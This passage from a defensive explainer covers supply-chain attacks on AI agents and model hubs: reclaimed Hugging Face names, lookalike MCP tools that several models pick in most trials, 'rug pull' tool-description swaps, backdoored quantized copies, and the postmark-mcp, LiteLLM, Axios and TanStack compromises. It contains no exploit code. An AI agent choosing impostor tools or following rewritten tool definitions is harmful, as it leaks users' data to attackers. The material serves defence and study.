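A correctly spelled name can also pass to a new owner. Saraf and Balassiano (2025), in *Model Namespace Reuse*, found that when an organisation deleted its Hugging Face account, anyone could register the name again. Software that loads a model by name would then download whatever the new owner had uploaded. Until someone registers the name, downloads fail, which alerts users. If the organisation moved its models to a new account before deleting the old one, users get no such warning, because Hugging Face redirects requests to the new location. An attacker can override the redirect by registering the old name and uploading a model there.

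Saraf and Balassiano, of the security company Palo Alto Networks, tested this on Google's Vertex AI, a service for running models. Vertex AI put a green check mark beside Hugging Face models that Google had verified for use there. Some models kept the mark after their publishers had disappeared. The researchers registered one of the abandoned names, uploaded a model containing their own code, and gained access to the isolated environment in which Vertex AI ran it. The same method worked on Microsoft's Azure AI Foundry. Thousands of public GitHub projects also referred to models whose names anyone could claim. Google now scans daily for models whose publishers have gone and blocks their deployment, though a daily scan could miss a name that someone claims within hours.

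Holzbauer and colleagues found seven abandoned GitHub repositories with the same weakness. Five of them supplied 77 skills listed on Skills.sh, and the other two supplied 44 on SkillsDirectory. The researchers registered the abandoned account names and checked whether GitHub would let them recreate the repositories, but did not recreate them. They have kept the accounts so that nobody else can take them. The affected skills on Skills.sh had a median of 25 downloads, but one had 2,032. There may be more such repositories, because the researchers tested only those with at least five stars. ClawHub is less exposed because it stores skills itself.

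Two tools can also share a name without anyone taking over an account. MCP requires tool names to be unique within a server but not across servers. Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026), in *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, connected five models to a legitimate server with a tool for fetching datasets, and to an attacker's server with one competing tool. They varied three parts of the attacker's tool:

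- its name, which was either unrelated or identical to the real one
- its description, which was unrelated, copied, or reworded to claim official approval
- its input fields, which either suited the request or did not

This gives 2 × 3 × 2 = 12 combinations. For each one, every model received ten wordings of the same request five times each, for 50 trials. The table shows how often the models chose the attacker's tool in five of the combinations.

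| Attacker's tool | Claude Sonnet 5 | DeepSeek V3 | Gemini 2.5 Pro | GPT-5.4 | Qwen3.7 Max |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Same name only | 0% | 0% | 0% | 2% | 0% |
| Same name and description | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Same name, suitable inputs | 0% | 28% | 60% | 12% | 40% |
| Same name and description, suitable inputs | 6% | 100% | 84% | 100% | 100% |
| Unrelated name, claim of approval, suitable inputs | 0% | 50% | 42% | 4% | 20% |

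A shared name alone almost never misled the models, but a full copy of the listing usually did. Three models chose the full copy every time, even though half of the requests stressed the trusted destination or the intended provider. Claude Sonnet 5 asked for clarification in 94% of trials with the full copy. Asking is safer, but the user then needs a way to tell the two tools apart.

The rates of 100% need some caution. If two listings look the same, choosing at random would give about 50%, so something else must have favoured the attacker's tool, possibly the order of the tools, which Anbiaee and colleagues don't report varying. They also tested only one kind of task. Still, a model can't identify the right provider from a listing that anyone can copy. The client software can identify which server each tool came from, and they recommend that it tie each tool to a verified provider.

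### What registries check

The MCP registry ties a server's name to an account or a domain. A publisher who logs in through GitHub as "alice" can publish only under names beginning "io.github.alice/". To use a domain instead, the publisher creates a pair of keys and puts the public one in the domain's settings or in a file on its website. The publisher then signs the current time with the private key, and the registry checks the signature against the public key. According to the Model Context Protocol's documentation, only an owner of a GitHub organisation can now publish under its name, though ordinary members could previously do so.

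According to OpenClaw's *Publishing*, every release on ClawHub has a named owner, and the site checks whether the publisher's access token has permission to publish for that owner. For plugins, which are code packages that extend OpenClaw, any owner's name at the start of the package name must also match the release's owner. OpenClaw staff can transfer or reserve disputed names after reviewing evidence. A user-written guide, ClawKit's *clawhub-publish-howto*, adds that the publisher's GitHub account must be at least 14 days old. This is a low barrier, since the accounts behind the stars that Shen and colleagues bought were about three weeks old.

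| Check | What it proves | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| MCP registry name | The publisher controlled the account or domain when publishing | Whether a familiar-looking name belongs to the company it suggests |
| GitHub Marketplace badge | The organisation controls a domain, has a confirmed email address and requires two-factor login | Whether its apps are safe |
| ClawHub owner | The publisher's token has permission to publish for that owner | Who the owner is, and whether someone stole the token |
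| Hugging Face verified organisation | A member has an email address at the organisation's domain | Whether the domain is the one users have in mind, and whether the files are safe |

None of these checks covers what the code does. GitHub's *About marketplace badges* warns that GitHub does not inspect third-party code. Singh's *The State of MCP Registries* points out that lookalike names also remain possible in the MCP registry.

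A verified-publisher badge can bring a component more users. Docker gives verified publishers priority in search results on Docker Hub, which now lists tool servers and models. If an agent tends to choose from the top of a list, a check on the publisher's identity will affect which code the agent runs.

### How a Sigstore signature works

Registry checks apply to the page from which a user downloads a file. A digital signature stays with the file, so users can check it wherever they got their copy. In the traditional method, a publisher keeps one private key for years and has to protect it from theft. Sigstore, a free signing service, avoids this with keys that last only minutes. Signing and checking a file takes five steps:

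1. The publisher logs in with an existing account, such as GitHub or Google. An automated workflow (a script that builds and publishes software) can instead prove its own identity to Sigstore.
2. The publisher's software creates a new pair of keys, and Sigstore issues a short-lived certificate that ties the public key to the account or workflow.
3. The software computes the file's hash, signs it with the private key and discards that key.
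4. Sigstore records the signing in Rekor, a public log that allows new entries but no changes to old ones.
5. The user's software recomputes the hash, checks the signature, certificate and log entry, and compares the identity in the certificate with the one the user expects.

The public log makes misuse easier to discover. If an intruder signs a file as someone else, the real owner can find the entry by monitoring the log.

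The final comparison is hard to automate because the identity in the certificate often changes between releases. For a workflow, the certificate names the repository, the workflow file and the branch or tag (a label for a particular version of the code). *A Difference Without a Distinction* examined packages with at least two releases signed in this way. A rule that raised an alert whenever any part of the identity changed flagged 75.8% of them, largely because the branch or tag had changed. Users would soon learn to ignore such alerts. Comparing only the repository and workflow file avoids many of them, but accepts a release from any branch.

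### Signing a model made of many files

A large model may consist of dozens of weights files, plus settings, a vocabulary and example code. In April 2025, Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues announced a tool that can sign a model of any size or format (*Launch of Model Signing v1.0*, 2025). The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), which hosts the project, published the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) specification in June. OpenSSF (2025) credits contributors from Google, NVIDIA, Meta, Microsoft and other companies.

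According to NVIDIA, OMS doesn't sign each file separately. It makes a manifest, which is a list of every file with its hash, and signs that:

manifest = (name₁, H(file₁)), (name₂, H(file₂)), …, (nameₙ, H(fileₙ))

signature = Sign(private key, H(manifest))

A publisher can sign a model by listing each file's hash in a manifest and signing the manifest's hash. If an intruder changes one setting in a file, that file's hash no longer matches the manifest. If the intruder also updates the manifest to match, the manifest's hash no longer matches the signature. The signature is a separate file, so the publisher doesn't have to alter the model to sign it. Publishers can use Sigstore, a certificate or an ordinary pair of keys. Red Hat's *Model authenticity and transparency with Sigstore* explains that with an ordinary pair, the user checks the signature against the public key of a known, trusted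 identity.

The checking software also has to reject any file that the manifest doesn't list, such as the program in the fake Privacy Filter repository. *Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications* (2026) describes a common practice of signing a model's weights but not the templates and settings around them, which can also change how the model behaves. The paper's attack fails if the publisher signs the whole release and the user checks all of it, but the paper describes this as rare on open model hubs.

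Many users run a quantized copy of a model, which stores each weight with fewer bits so that the model fits on an ordinary computer. Someone other than the original developer usually makes this copy. Liu and Tsai (2026), in *What You Sign Is Not What You Run*, point out that the developer's signature on the original files doesn't cover it. The person who made the copy can sign it, but that signature would be just as valid on a copy with a backdoor. Liu and Tsai examined 198 of the most downloaded repositories of such copies, from 61 publishers. None recorded enough detail for an outsider to repeat the conversion and confirm that the copy was faithful.

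### A valid signature from an impostor

Suppose a bookkeeper wants a database server from Tallyfield, a fictional company with the GitHub account "tallyfield". An impostor opens the account "tallyfield-hq", copies Tallyfield's code and README, and adds a few lines that steal passwords. The impostor then publishes the result through an automated workflow.

Sigstore issues a certificate, because the workflow really does belong to tallyfield-hq. The MCP registry accepts the name "io.github.tallyfield-hq/db-server" for the same reason. The bookkeeper's software finds that the hash matches, the signature and certificate are valid, and the log contains the right entry. Only the comparison of identities reveals the problem:

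```
expected: github.com/tallyfield/db-server/.github/workflows/release.yml
found:    github.com/tallyfield-hq/db-server/.github/workflows/release.yml
```

If Tallyfield and every impostor sign their releases, the likelihood ratio of impostor to Tallyfield for "has a valid signature" is 1/1, so the signature is no evidence about who published the server. A signature from tallyfield's own workflow is evidence, because an impostor would have to break into the account or the workflow to get one. If one impostor in a thousand managed that, and Tallyfield always signed through its workflow, the ratio would be 0.001.

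The bookkeeper therefore has to find out beforehand whose signature to expect, from somewhere other than the download page. If the expected identity comes from an impostor's README, the impostor's signature will match it. Better sources are an invoice from Tallyfield, its established website or a list kept by someone who has already investigated. Stacklok keeps such a list for its ToolHive software. For GitHub's tool server, the list records the expected repository, workflow and certificate issuer. People who use the list don't have to investigate each publisher themselves, but a mistake in it affects them all.

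An agent that searches for "a database server" without an expected publisher has nothing to compare the signer's identity against. It can confirm that some account signed the file, but an impostor's signed file would pass the same check.

*Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) notes that even the expected signature covers a hidden routine, or a compromised package the server relies on, just as it covers the rest of the release.

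### Who signs, and who checks

Signing is fairly common among actively maintained packages. *A Difference Without a Distinction* found that 43% of sampled npm packages and 40% of sampled PyPI packages had at least one release with a signature tied to a workflow identity. The samples exclude packages with fewer than four releases between April 2024 and September 2026, so the shares for all packages are probably lower. On RubyGems, the Ruby catalogue, only about 6% of releases had such signatures. Maven Central, a Java catalogue, requires a signature on every file, but these signatures use the older kind of long-lived key. The npm registry also signs every package with its own key, which helps show that a file came from npm but not who wrote it.

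The clearest example for models is NVIDIA, which signs everything it publishes in its NGC catalogue. HiddenLayer, a security company that helps lead the model-signing project, reports that Google's Kaggle is also adopting the OMS format.

Tool servers are further behind. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, states that the protocol gives clients no built-in way to check whether a tool's listing or code has changed since the user approved it. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (2026), which proposes adding signed documents to the protocol, says that today's public servers don't publish such documents. Some servers are signed outside the protocol, including the GitHub server on Stacklok's list.

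Even where signatures exist, software often leaves the checking to the user. NVIDIA's software automatically compares downloaded files with their expected hashes, but NVIDIA's *Model Signature Verification* describes the signature check as a separate procedure, in which the user has to find the exact model version, download the model, its signature and NVIDIA's certificate, and run another program. ToolHive checks signatures automatically, but by default it only warns the user if the check fails. The package manager pnpm can refuse a release with weaker evidence of origin than earlier ones, but this setting is off by default. *A Difference Without a Distinction* found 4,516 public GitHub repositories that had turned it on.

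### The burden on anonymous volunteers

Volunteers write a lot of useful software, and some have good reasons to stay anonymous, such as fear of harassment or of an employer or government that disapproves of their work. Identity checks can expose them even when a registry doesn't mean to publish anything. Holzbauer and colleagues found that ClawHub's programming interface revealed the email addresses linked to publishers' GitHub accounts, which GitHub profiles don't show by default. Sigstore creates a more lasting risk because, if a volunteer signs with an email account, the address appears in the certificate and the public log keeps it permanently.

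This is a strong argument against requiring legal names, but a much weaker one against signatures. A volunteer can sign through a workflow on a pseudonymous GitHub account, so the certificate names the repository and not a person. The OMS format also accepts a plain key pair with no name. Users can then confirm that a new release comes from the same source as the previous one, which is often what they most need to know about a volunteer's project. A signature is little help with the first release, because users don't yet have a reason to trust the pseudonym.

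A volunteer still has to learn the tools, and may have to rely on GitHub, because ClawHub's method for publishing plugins without a stored token supports only GitHub's workflows. Badges that require a domain favour companies, and Docker's search priority then brings them more users. A registry could reduce this unfairness by requiring every publisher to keep a consistent identity, while making real-world verification optional and giving it no weight in search rankings. Impostors could still open pseudonymous accounts, but they can already register a domain and get a badge for it.

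## Changes made after a component has been approved

An identity check can show that a new release comes from the same publisher as the last one, but the code may still have changed. A review covers only the version the reviewer read. If someone reviews version 1.4 of a tool server and version 1.5 comes out the next day, nobody has reviewed the changes.

A record of harmless releases is weak evidence that the next one is safe. An honest publisher would almost certainly have a record of 15 harmless versions, but so would an attacker who planned to turn malicious in the next one, so the likelihood ratio is close to 1. The record does rule out attackers who would have struck sooner, and few would spend ten years building a record for a single theft. But someone who steals an established publisher's account gets its record without that work.

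### The postmark-mcp case

In September 2025, an npm package called postmark-mcp offered agents a tool server for sending email through Postmark, which delivers email for other companies' software. According to Koi, the security company that discovered the attack, the first 15 versions worked as described. Version 1.0.16 added one line of code that sent a hidden copy of every email to the developer's server. The original emails still went out normally, so agents had no sign that anything was wrong.

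The developer seemed reputable. Koi found a software engineer in Paris who used a real name and had a GitHub profile full of legitimate projects. Koi warns that a tool can behave well for months before it turns malicious, but this one turned sooner. The Hacker News (2025) reports that the developer uploaded the package on 15 September and released version 1.0.16 on 17 September. The 15 clean versions covered only about two days, which shows that a long list of versions is nearly as easy to produce as a high star count.

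Checking the publisher would have helped here. The developer had copied the code for Postmark's real server from GitHub, and Postmark says it had not published that server on npm before the incident.

Nobody knows how many emails the developer collected. Koi estimated 3,000 to 15,000 a day. It started from 1,500 downloads a week, guessed that 300 organisations were using the package, and assumed that each sent 10 to 50 emails a day. But the package had only 1,643 downloads in total, and some of those may have been of clean versions or made by automated systems. The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi made contact, but this did not stop the copies already installed.

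Postmark's genuine server has changed far more than the fake one did. It grew from 4 tools to 24 in about a year, according to Postmark's blog. An approval given at the start covered little more than sending email, so even a legitimate update can make an approval out of date.

### How often registry entries change

The 2026 census of the MCP registry compared successive versions of the 8,900 servers that had more than one. Kraishan found that 51.1% of them had changed their description, packages or remote endpoint (the address where an agent sends its requests). In 40.6%, at least one change was silent drift, meaning that the server's description or endpoint changed while its name and identifiers stayed the same. The endpoint moved to a different host in 370 cases (4.2%).

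Kraishan counts any rewritten description as silent drift, even if the publisher only corrected a typo, and 36.4% of the servers had a rewritten description. Kraishan's percentages exclude the 12,743 servers with a single version. Across the whole registry, about 21% of servers changed and 1.7% moved their endpoint. Among those that changed, the median time to the first change was zero days, so many publishers were probably correcting a listing they had just posted.

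Bharti (2026), in *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, followed the same registry for 89 days and found that most entries were stable. About three quarters never changed, and only 11.9% changed within 30 days. This is much lower than the daily rate of change suggests. On a typical day 1.465% of entries changed, and if every entry were equally likely to change, the share changed after 30 days would be:

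1 − (1 − 0.01465)^30 ≈ 0.358

The real figure is a third of that because the same servers change repeatedly. The most active 5% made 61% of all the changes.

Bharti also runs a scanner that assesses servers by their registry descriptions. Of its 18,543 current verdicts, 747 applied to descriptions that were no longer in the registry. In about half of these cases, the publisher had changed the description after the scan. In the rest, the scanner had used a copy that was already outdated.

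Storing a hash of each server's description, and reviewing the description again when the hash changes, works better than rechecking the servers that change most often. It would require about 39 reviews a day, compared with 2,700 a day to reread the whole registry every week. If Bharti rechecked only the 5% of servers with the most past changes, the reviews would catch about 20% of the known servers whose descriptions changed next, and none of the newly added ones.

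### Silent drift and serious findings

Servers with silent drift had 2.96 times the odds of a high-severity finding in Kraishan's scan. Odds are the probability that something is true divided by the probability that it isn't. Suppose 10% of servers without silent drift have such a finding:

odds without drift = 0.10 / 0.90 ≈ 0.111

odds with drift = 0.111 × 2.96 ≈ 0.329

probability with drift = 0.329 / 1.329 ≈ 0.25

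In this example, a server with silent drift is two and a half times as likely to have a serious weakness.

This is only a correlation. Kraishan suggests that careless publishers both rewrite their listings often and write weaker code. Age and size could also contribute, since the comparison doesn't adjust for them. Older servers have had more time to change, and Kraishan found more weaknesses in older and larger servers. Servers with a remote endpoint also have an extra field that can change, and they had more high-severity findings than servers without one. Drift is therefore a reasonable way to decide which servers to inspect first, but editing a listing less often would not make the server's code safer.

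Most of the 370 endpoint moves were probably innocent, since companies change hosting providers, adopt new domains and replace test addresses with permanent ones. Kraishan expects that most were routine but did not investigate them individually. If 10 of 10,000 servers were malicious and all 10 moved, along with 4% of the 9,990 honest ones, there would be about 400 honest moves and 10 malicious ones, so about 98% of the moves would be innocent. A user still has reason to check a move, because the registry entry looks the same whether the owner changed hosts or an attacker took over the listing.

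### Tool definitions are missing from the registry

The registry keeps no history of tool definitions (each tool's name, description and input format). None of the 72,606 version records in the census contains a tool definition. An agent gets the definitions directly from the server when it connects, so a publisher can rewrite them without creating a new registry version. The description in the registry, which is limited to 100 characters, can stay the same.

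*MCP-38* describes a server that passes a security review with harmless tool descriptions and then replaces them with malicious ones. Security researchers call this a "rug pull", and the WhatsApp demonstration worked this way. The protocol lets a server announce that its tools have changed. But according to *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026), the protocol doesn't require the agent's software to ask the user for consent again. A malicious server could also change its tools without announcing it.

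### Pinning and Docker's catalogue

Pinning means accepting only one exact version of a component, identified by a hash or a commit. A commit is a recorded state of a project's source code, and its identifier is computed from the contents. A label such as "latest" is not a pin, because it can later refer to different code. Nor is a version tag on GitHub, which can be deleted and recreated to point to other code.

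Docker's catalogue of tool servers uses commits to tie each review to particular code. Docker (2025) describes the process for local servers that it builds itself:

1. The catalogue entry names a source repository and a commit, and an automated check rejects any entry without one.
2. Every night, a program looks for newer commits and proposes an update for each server that has one.
3. Two AI programming agents, Claude Code and OpenAI Codex, review the changes and write a report that rates the risk.
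4. A critical finding blocks the update. Docker's staff read the reports and make the final decision.
5. Docker builds the server and records the commit in the finished package, where users can look it up and check it against Docker's signature.

In one example, the agents reviewed 23 commits to a toolkit from the payments company Stripe and rated the overall risk medium. Docker gives the agents no passwords or direct internet access, because the code under review could contain instructions meant to manipulate them.

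This solves part of the problem with old approvals, because each review covers a specific version of the code, and new code needs another review. The reviews may still miss things. Docker reported that the reviews had found security mistakes but nothing malicious, so there was no evidence yet of how well they would catch a real attack. Docker also planned to approve most updates automatically. A user who always runs the latest package from the catalogue has not pinned a version and relies on Docker's approval of each update.

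Pinning a tool server doesn't necessarily pin the packages it depends on. He, Vasilescu and Kästner (2025), in *Pinning Is Futile*, simulated what would happen if npm projects pinned only the packages they use directly. Their model estimates how this changes the number of dependencies that can still update automatically, where N is the total number of dependencies:

multiplier ≈ exp(−0.519 + 0.084 ln N)

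With 20 dependencies the number falls by about 23%, with about 500 it stays the same, and with 2,000 it rises by about 13%. A likely reason for the increase is that npm installs extra copies of a package when different parts of a project need different versions, and each copy brings its own dependencies. A lock file, which records the exact version of every dependency, avoids this problem for an application, but npm ignores a package's own lock file when someone else installs the package as a dependency.

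The main drawback of pinning is that it blocks security fixes along with malicious updates. In the simulation, where nobody updated anything by hand for a year, pinning raised the average number of dependencies with known vulnerabilities from 2.13 to 2.70. Pinning is therefore safer only if someone keeps reviewing new versions and updating the pinned version.

### Asking for consent again

An agent's software can also store the tool definitions that the user approved, compare them with what the server sends at each connection, and require new approval if anything differs. It should compare the exact text that the model receives, because the approval screen may leave out part of it.

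This would expose a rug pull like the WhatsApp one. It would probably have missed postmark-mcp, because the developer changed the program and, according to Koi, nothing else. It also doesn't protect against definitions that were malicious from the start.

Warning users every time an approved component changes interrupts them frequently. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026) examined the version histories of 515 tool servers and found that publishers routinely add tools, reword descriptions and make optional inputs compulsory. Users who see a warning for every reworded sentence may start approving changes without reading them. The software could reduce this risk by showing only what changed, and by displaying a new tool that can send data more prominently than a spelling correction.

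Asking users for consent again when an endpoint moves would interrupt them much less often. Kraishan recorded 441 such moves in eleven months across the whole registry, so a user with ten servers might not see one all year. Kraishan recommends that the registry treat a new host as a major change that needs fresh consent, and that agents' software remember the original host in the meantime. The user would still have to check whether the new address belongs to the publisher, for example on the company's established website. Asking again after a move also wouldn't catch an attacker who takes control of the original host, since they don't need to move the endpoint.

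### Waiting before taking a new release

Waiting a few days before installing a new release gives other people time to discover whether it is malicious. The 41 malicious releases in *A Difference Without a Distinction* stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours. A one-day wait would have kept out 36 of them, and a seven-day wait 40.

In July 2026, GitHub changed Dependabot, its tool for proposing updates to the packages a project uses, to wait three days by default before proposing a new version (GitHub, *Dependabot version updates introduce default package cooldown*, 2026). Few projects had chosen to wait before then; *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues, 2026) found a waiting period in 135 of 1,462 popular repositories that used Dependabot, most often seven days. A Dependabot setting doesn't affect someone who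 installs a tool server by hand, but *package managers need to cool down* (2026) reports that npm, pip and several other installers now have waiting periods of their own.

Waiting to install a new release works less well if few people are checking it. The public malware record for postmark-mcp, OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), appeared on 26 September, nine days after the malicious release. A user who waited seven days could have installed it before that warning. GitHub's *The case for a cooldown* also acknowledges that waiting does little against a backdoor that stays dormant or a maintainer who sabotages their own project.

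*Dependency cooldowns turn you into a free-rider* objects that people who delay installing new releases rely on others to take the risk first. This is partly true, but an attack can sometimes be discovered before it has a victim. Koi found postmark-mcp because its monitoring software flagged a change in the package's behaviour. The essay proposes that registries hold every release in a queue before anyone can install it, and notify the project's maintainers. This would warn maintainers if someone had stolen their account and published a release, but it would not stop an attack by the developer.

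The most serious drawback of waiting is again that it delays security fixes. Attackers exploited a critical flaw in Langflow, a framework for building agents, within 20 hours of its disclosure, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Hackers Exploit Critical Langflow Bug in Just 20 Hours*. If a fix came out with the disclosure, a user who waited three days to install it would have been exposed to these attacks for more than two days.

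Dependabot therefore doesn't apply the wait to security updates. But it recognises a security update only after someone has published an advisory about the flaw, and a fix may come out before that. *A Fine-Grained Empirical Study of Upstream Security Events and Downstream Mitigation* (2026) found a median delay of 73.2 days in adopting security fixes among Java projects that used Dependabot's security updates, compared with 10.4 days among those set up for regular version updates. The second group may simply be better maintained, but Dependabot also proposes fixes to those projects without waiting for an advisory.

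### Why users cannot pin a remote server

A user can pin a local server because its code is on the user's own computer. With a remote server, the user sees only the responses. The operator can publish the source code and its hash, but the user cannot ordinarily confirm that the server runs that code, or runs the same code for everyone. Special hardware that can attest to the software it runs may provide some evidence, but few users can rely on this today.

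The user can still pin a remote server's address and tool definitions, but pinning them does not reveal a change in what the operator does with the data. It is safer to run a local copy if the publisher offers one, or to give the server a password that allows access only to what the task needs. If postmark-mcp had been a remote server, its developer could have started copying emails without releasing a new version, and Koi would have had no changed package to examine.

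## Records of how a component was built

Even a pinned package can differ from the source code that people reviewed. An intruder can add code while the source is being built into an installable package, or upload a different package instead. Reading the public source won't reveal either change.

Build provenance is a signed record of the source, machine and steps used to build a particular file. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts), an OpenSSF project, defines a common format for these records and grades how far users can rely on them.

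### What the record contains

Suppose Tallyfield, the fictional maker of the database server, releases version 1.5 through an automated workflow on GitHub. Put simply, the build record would contain:

```
file:      db-server-1.5.tgz, with its SHA-256 hash
source:    github.com/tallyfield/db-server
version:   refs/tags/v1.5, with the full commit identifier
workflow:  .github/workflows/release.yml
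builder:   GitHub Actions, on a machine run by GitHub
run:       a run number, with start and finish times
```

The builder is the most important entry in the record because the accuracy of the other entries depends on it. In SLSA's format, it stands for everyone and everything that users must trust to run the build and fill in the record, including the platform's staff and hardware. Users should accept a record only if they trust its signer to sign for that builder. For example, GitHub can sign records for GitHub Actions but not for Google's build service.

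The SLSA format separates settings chosen by whoever started the build, such as the repository and branch, from settings controlled by the platform. Users already trust the platform, so they only have to check the chosen settings, because an intruder might start a genuine build from the wrong branch. The record can also list packages that the build downloaded, but SLSA asks only for a best effort to make this list complete, so a missing package may still have been part of the build.

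### Checking a record against a policy

SLSA's *Build* guidance recommends checking a build record in these steps:

1. Check the signature, and look up the builder in a list of builders the user trusts.
2. Compare the hash in the record with the hash of the downloaded file.
3. Compare the source repository, the type of build and the chosen settings with the expected values, and reject any setting that the policy doesn't mention.
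4. If practical, check the packages used in the build in the same way.

A policy for Tallyfield might accept only files that GitHub Actions built from tallyfield/db-server, using release.yml and a version tag. It would reject the impostor's package from tallyfield-hq. It would also reject a file that a thief uploaded from a laptop, because that file would have no record from GitHub Actions.

As with signatures, the expected values have to come from a source that an intruder can't easily alter. In the Go programming language, a package's name is the address of its repository, so the name gives the expected source. A user can also accept the first version's record and investigate if a later one differs, but this fails if the first version is malicious.

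A registry can check records before it accepts an upload, which protects all its users. Checking again at download protects against someone who has broken into the registry.

### The SLSA build levels

SLSA's *Build* specification defines four levels:

| Level | Requirement | How hard the record is to forge |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | None | There may be no record |
| 1 | A record of how the publisher built the package, possibly unsigned | Trivial |
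| 2 | A hosted build platform creates and signs the record | Takes a deliberate attack, which may be easy |
| 3 | The platform also isolates builds and protects the signing secrets | Takes a flaw that most attackers could not exploit |

Level 3 adds two controls to Level 2. The platform must prevent builds from influencing one another, even within the same project, and must prevent the build steps that developers write from accessing the secrets used to sign records.

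Without these controls, malicious code that gets into one build could tamper with the next one or sign a record for a file of its own. A Level 2 record therefore protects a file against changes after the build, while Level 3 also protects it against tampering during the build. Level 3 doesn't cover a malicious insider at the build platform, and no build level covers what the source code does.

### Trusted publishing

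Registries have traditionally accepted uploads from anyone with a publishing token, a long-lived secret that works like a password. npm and PyPI now also offer trusted publishing, in which a publisher tells the registry which repository and workflow may release a package. When that workflow runs, the build platform issues a short-lived token identifying it. The registry accepts the upload if the token matches the registered repository and workflow, so the publisher doesn't have to store a long-lived secret that someone could steal.

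Trusted publishing controls who can upload a package, and provenance is a record of how the package was built, which users can check afterwards. npm marks packages that have provenance, and its "npm audit signatures" command checks the records, according to the programming blog Adventures in Nodeland.

In spring 2026, attackers published malicious versions of several widely used packages. Build records would have helped in only one of the cases below.

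| Attack | How the attacker published | Record on normal releases | Record on malicious release |
|---|---|---|---|
| LiteLLM, 24 March | Direct upload, probably with a stolen token | Probably none | Probably none |
| Axios 1.14.1, 31 March | Direct upload from a hijacked account | Yes | No |
| TanStack, 11 May | The project's own release workflow | Yes | Yes, and valid |

### LiteLLM and Axios

LiteLLM is a Python package that lets programs use many companies' models through one interface. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), malicious versions 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 were available from 10:39 UTC for about 40 minutes before PyPI quarantined them. These versions searched for passwords, cloud credentials and other secrets and sent what they found to the attackers. Some people could have installed the malicious versions without choosing LiteLLM, because agent frameworks and tool servers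 depend on it.

In *Security Townhall Updates*, LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, Dholakia and Jaff (2026), say they believe the publishing token was stolen through a compromised copy of Trivy, a security scanner that ran during LiteLLM's builds. LiteLLM had not pinned the scanner's version, and every build step could read the token. The attackers then bypassed LiteLLM's build process and uploaded their packages directly to PyPI.

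LiteLLM started moving to trusted publishing only after the attack, so earlier versions probably had no build records. A user who noticed that version 1.82.7 had none would therefore have had little reason to worry. The company later compared 20 earlier PyPI releases by hand with the corresponding commits in its public repository, a check that build records are meant to make easy, and found that all of them matched.

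Axios, a JavaScript library for sending web requests, had already adopted trusted publishing for its main series of releases when an attacker deceived its lead maintainer. According to the maintainer's report, which Solar Designer (2026) copied to a security mailing list in *Axios Supply-Chain Attack*, the attacker used a fake company with a convincing Slack workspace and a video meeting. During the meeting, the maintainer installed what seemed to be a missing update, which gave the attacker control of the maintainer's computer.

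Datadog Security Labs' *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (2026) reproduces npm's data about the axios releases. npm recorded GitHub Actions as the publisher of version 1.14.0 and included a trusted-publisher entry. It recorded the maintainer's personal account as the publisher of the malicious version 1.14.1, with a new email address and no trusted-publisher entry. VentureBeat reports that the security company Endor Labs found build provenance on 1.14.0 and none on 1.14.1. A check for missing provenance would therefore have caught 1.14.1, but npm accepted the upload.

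Checking for a change between releases would probably have missed the second malicious release, 0.30.4. The maintainer said that the older 0.x series still used a long-lived token, so a missing trusted-publisher entry was normal in that series.

Adventures in Nodeland argues that provenance would not have helped Axios, because the attacker had taken over the real maintainer's session and any record would have confirmed that the right person published the package. npm's data contradict this for version 1.14.1, which the attacker uploaded without the usual record. The argument still has some merit, because Datadog Security Labs found that the attacker also controlled the maintainer's GitHub account, and so might have been able to publish through the real workflow and get a valid record. The attacker did not need to try this, because npm still allowed direct uploads.

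To benefit from trusted publishing, a project also has to disable its old publishing method. pnpm has an optional check that refuses a release with weaker evidence of origin than earlier releases, and it should have blocked version 1.14.1 for users who had turned it on.

### Valid records on malicious TanStack releases

TanStack is a family of JavaScript libraries for building websites. OSV's *GHSA-g7cv-rxg3-hmpx* (2026) records 84 malicious versions of 42 TanStack packages, published within about six minutes. They stole credentials and tried to infect other packages that the victim maintained. According to SLSA, the attack spread to more than 170 packages, including some published under the name of the AI company Mistral. One victim, the software company Grafana Labs, reported in *Post-incident review for TanStack npm supply chain ransom incident* (2026) that the damage was limited to its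 GitHub environment and did not reach customers' production systems.

The attacker planted code in a cache, a store of files that different workflows reuse to save time. TanStack's real release workflow later loaded the code, which stole the workflow's short-lived publishing token and used it to upload the malicious packages. The attacker did not steal a permanent npm token. The workflow had permission to publish many packages, so the attacker could release all of them within minutes.

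The malicious TanStack packages had valid provenance, with the correct repository, workflow, branch and builder. A user who checked all four against a policy would have accepted the packages. TanStack's genuine releases had the same kind of record, so the likelihood ratio for valid provenance was 1 in this case.

SLSA says npm's built-in provenance reaches only Level 2, although several reports described these records as Level 3. Level 3 explicitly requires a platform to stop one build from planting false entries in a cache that another build uses. SLSA concludes that a platform meeting this requirement would have blocked the attack.

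SLSA is assessing its own framework here, so it has an interest in finding that the build platform failed rather than the framework. Its conclusion about the cache is convincing, since the requirement describes almost exactly what went wrong. It is less certain that Level 3 would have kept this attacker out altogether, because SLSA acknowledges that the unsafe workflow setting that let the attacker in is outside its scope, and that attackers have used the same kind of mistake to steal publishing credentials in other ways.

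TanStack's users also could not have protected themselves just by demanding Level 3, because that policy would have rejected the project's genuine releases along with the malicious ones. The project and its build platform had to make the change.

The one visible warning was that both workflow runs that published malicious packages ended with the status "failed", because a test failed after the attacker's code had started running. Standard provenance tools don't check this status. SLSA suggests an alert whenever a failed run publishes a package, and estimates that it could have shortened the exposure by hours. Outside researchers noticed the attack within about 20 minutes, according to InfoQ's *TanStack Details Sophisticated npm Supply Chain Attack That Compromised 42 Packages* (2026), so the alert could have sped up detection only slightly, and most of any reduction in exposure would have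 to come from removing the packages sooner. TanStack acknowledged that the malware broke the tests by accident, so a more careful attacker could have avoided this alert.

### Reproducible builds and independent rebuilders

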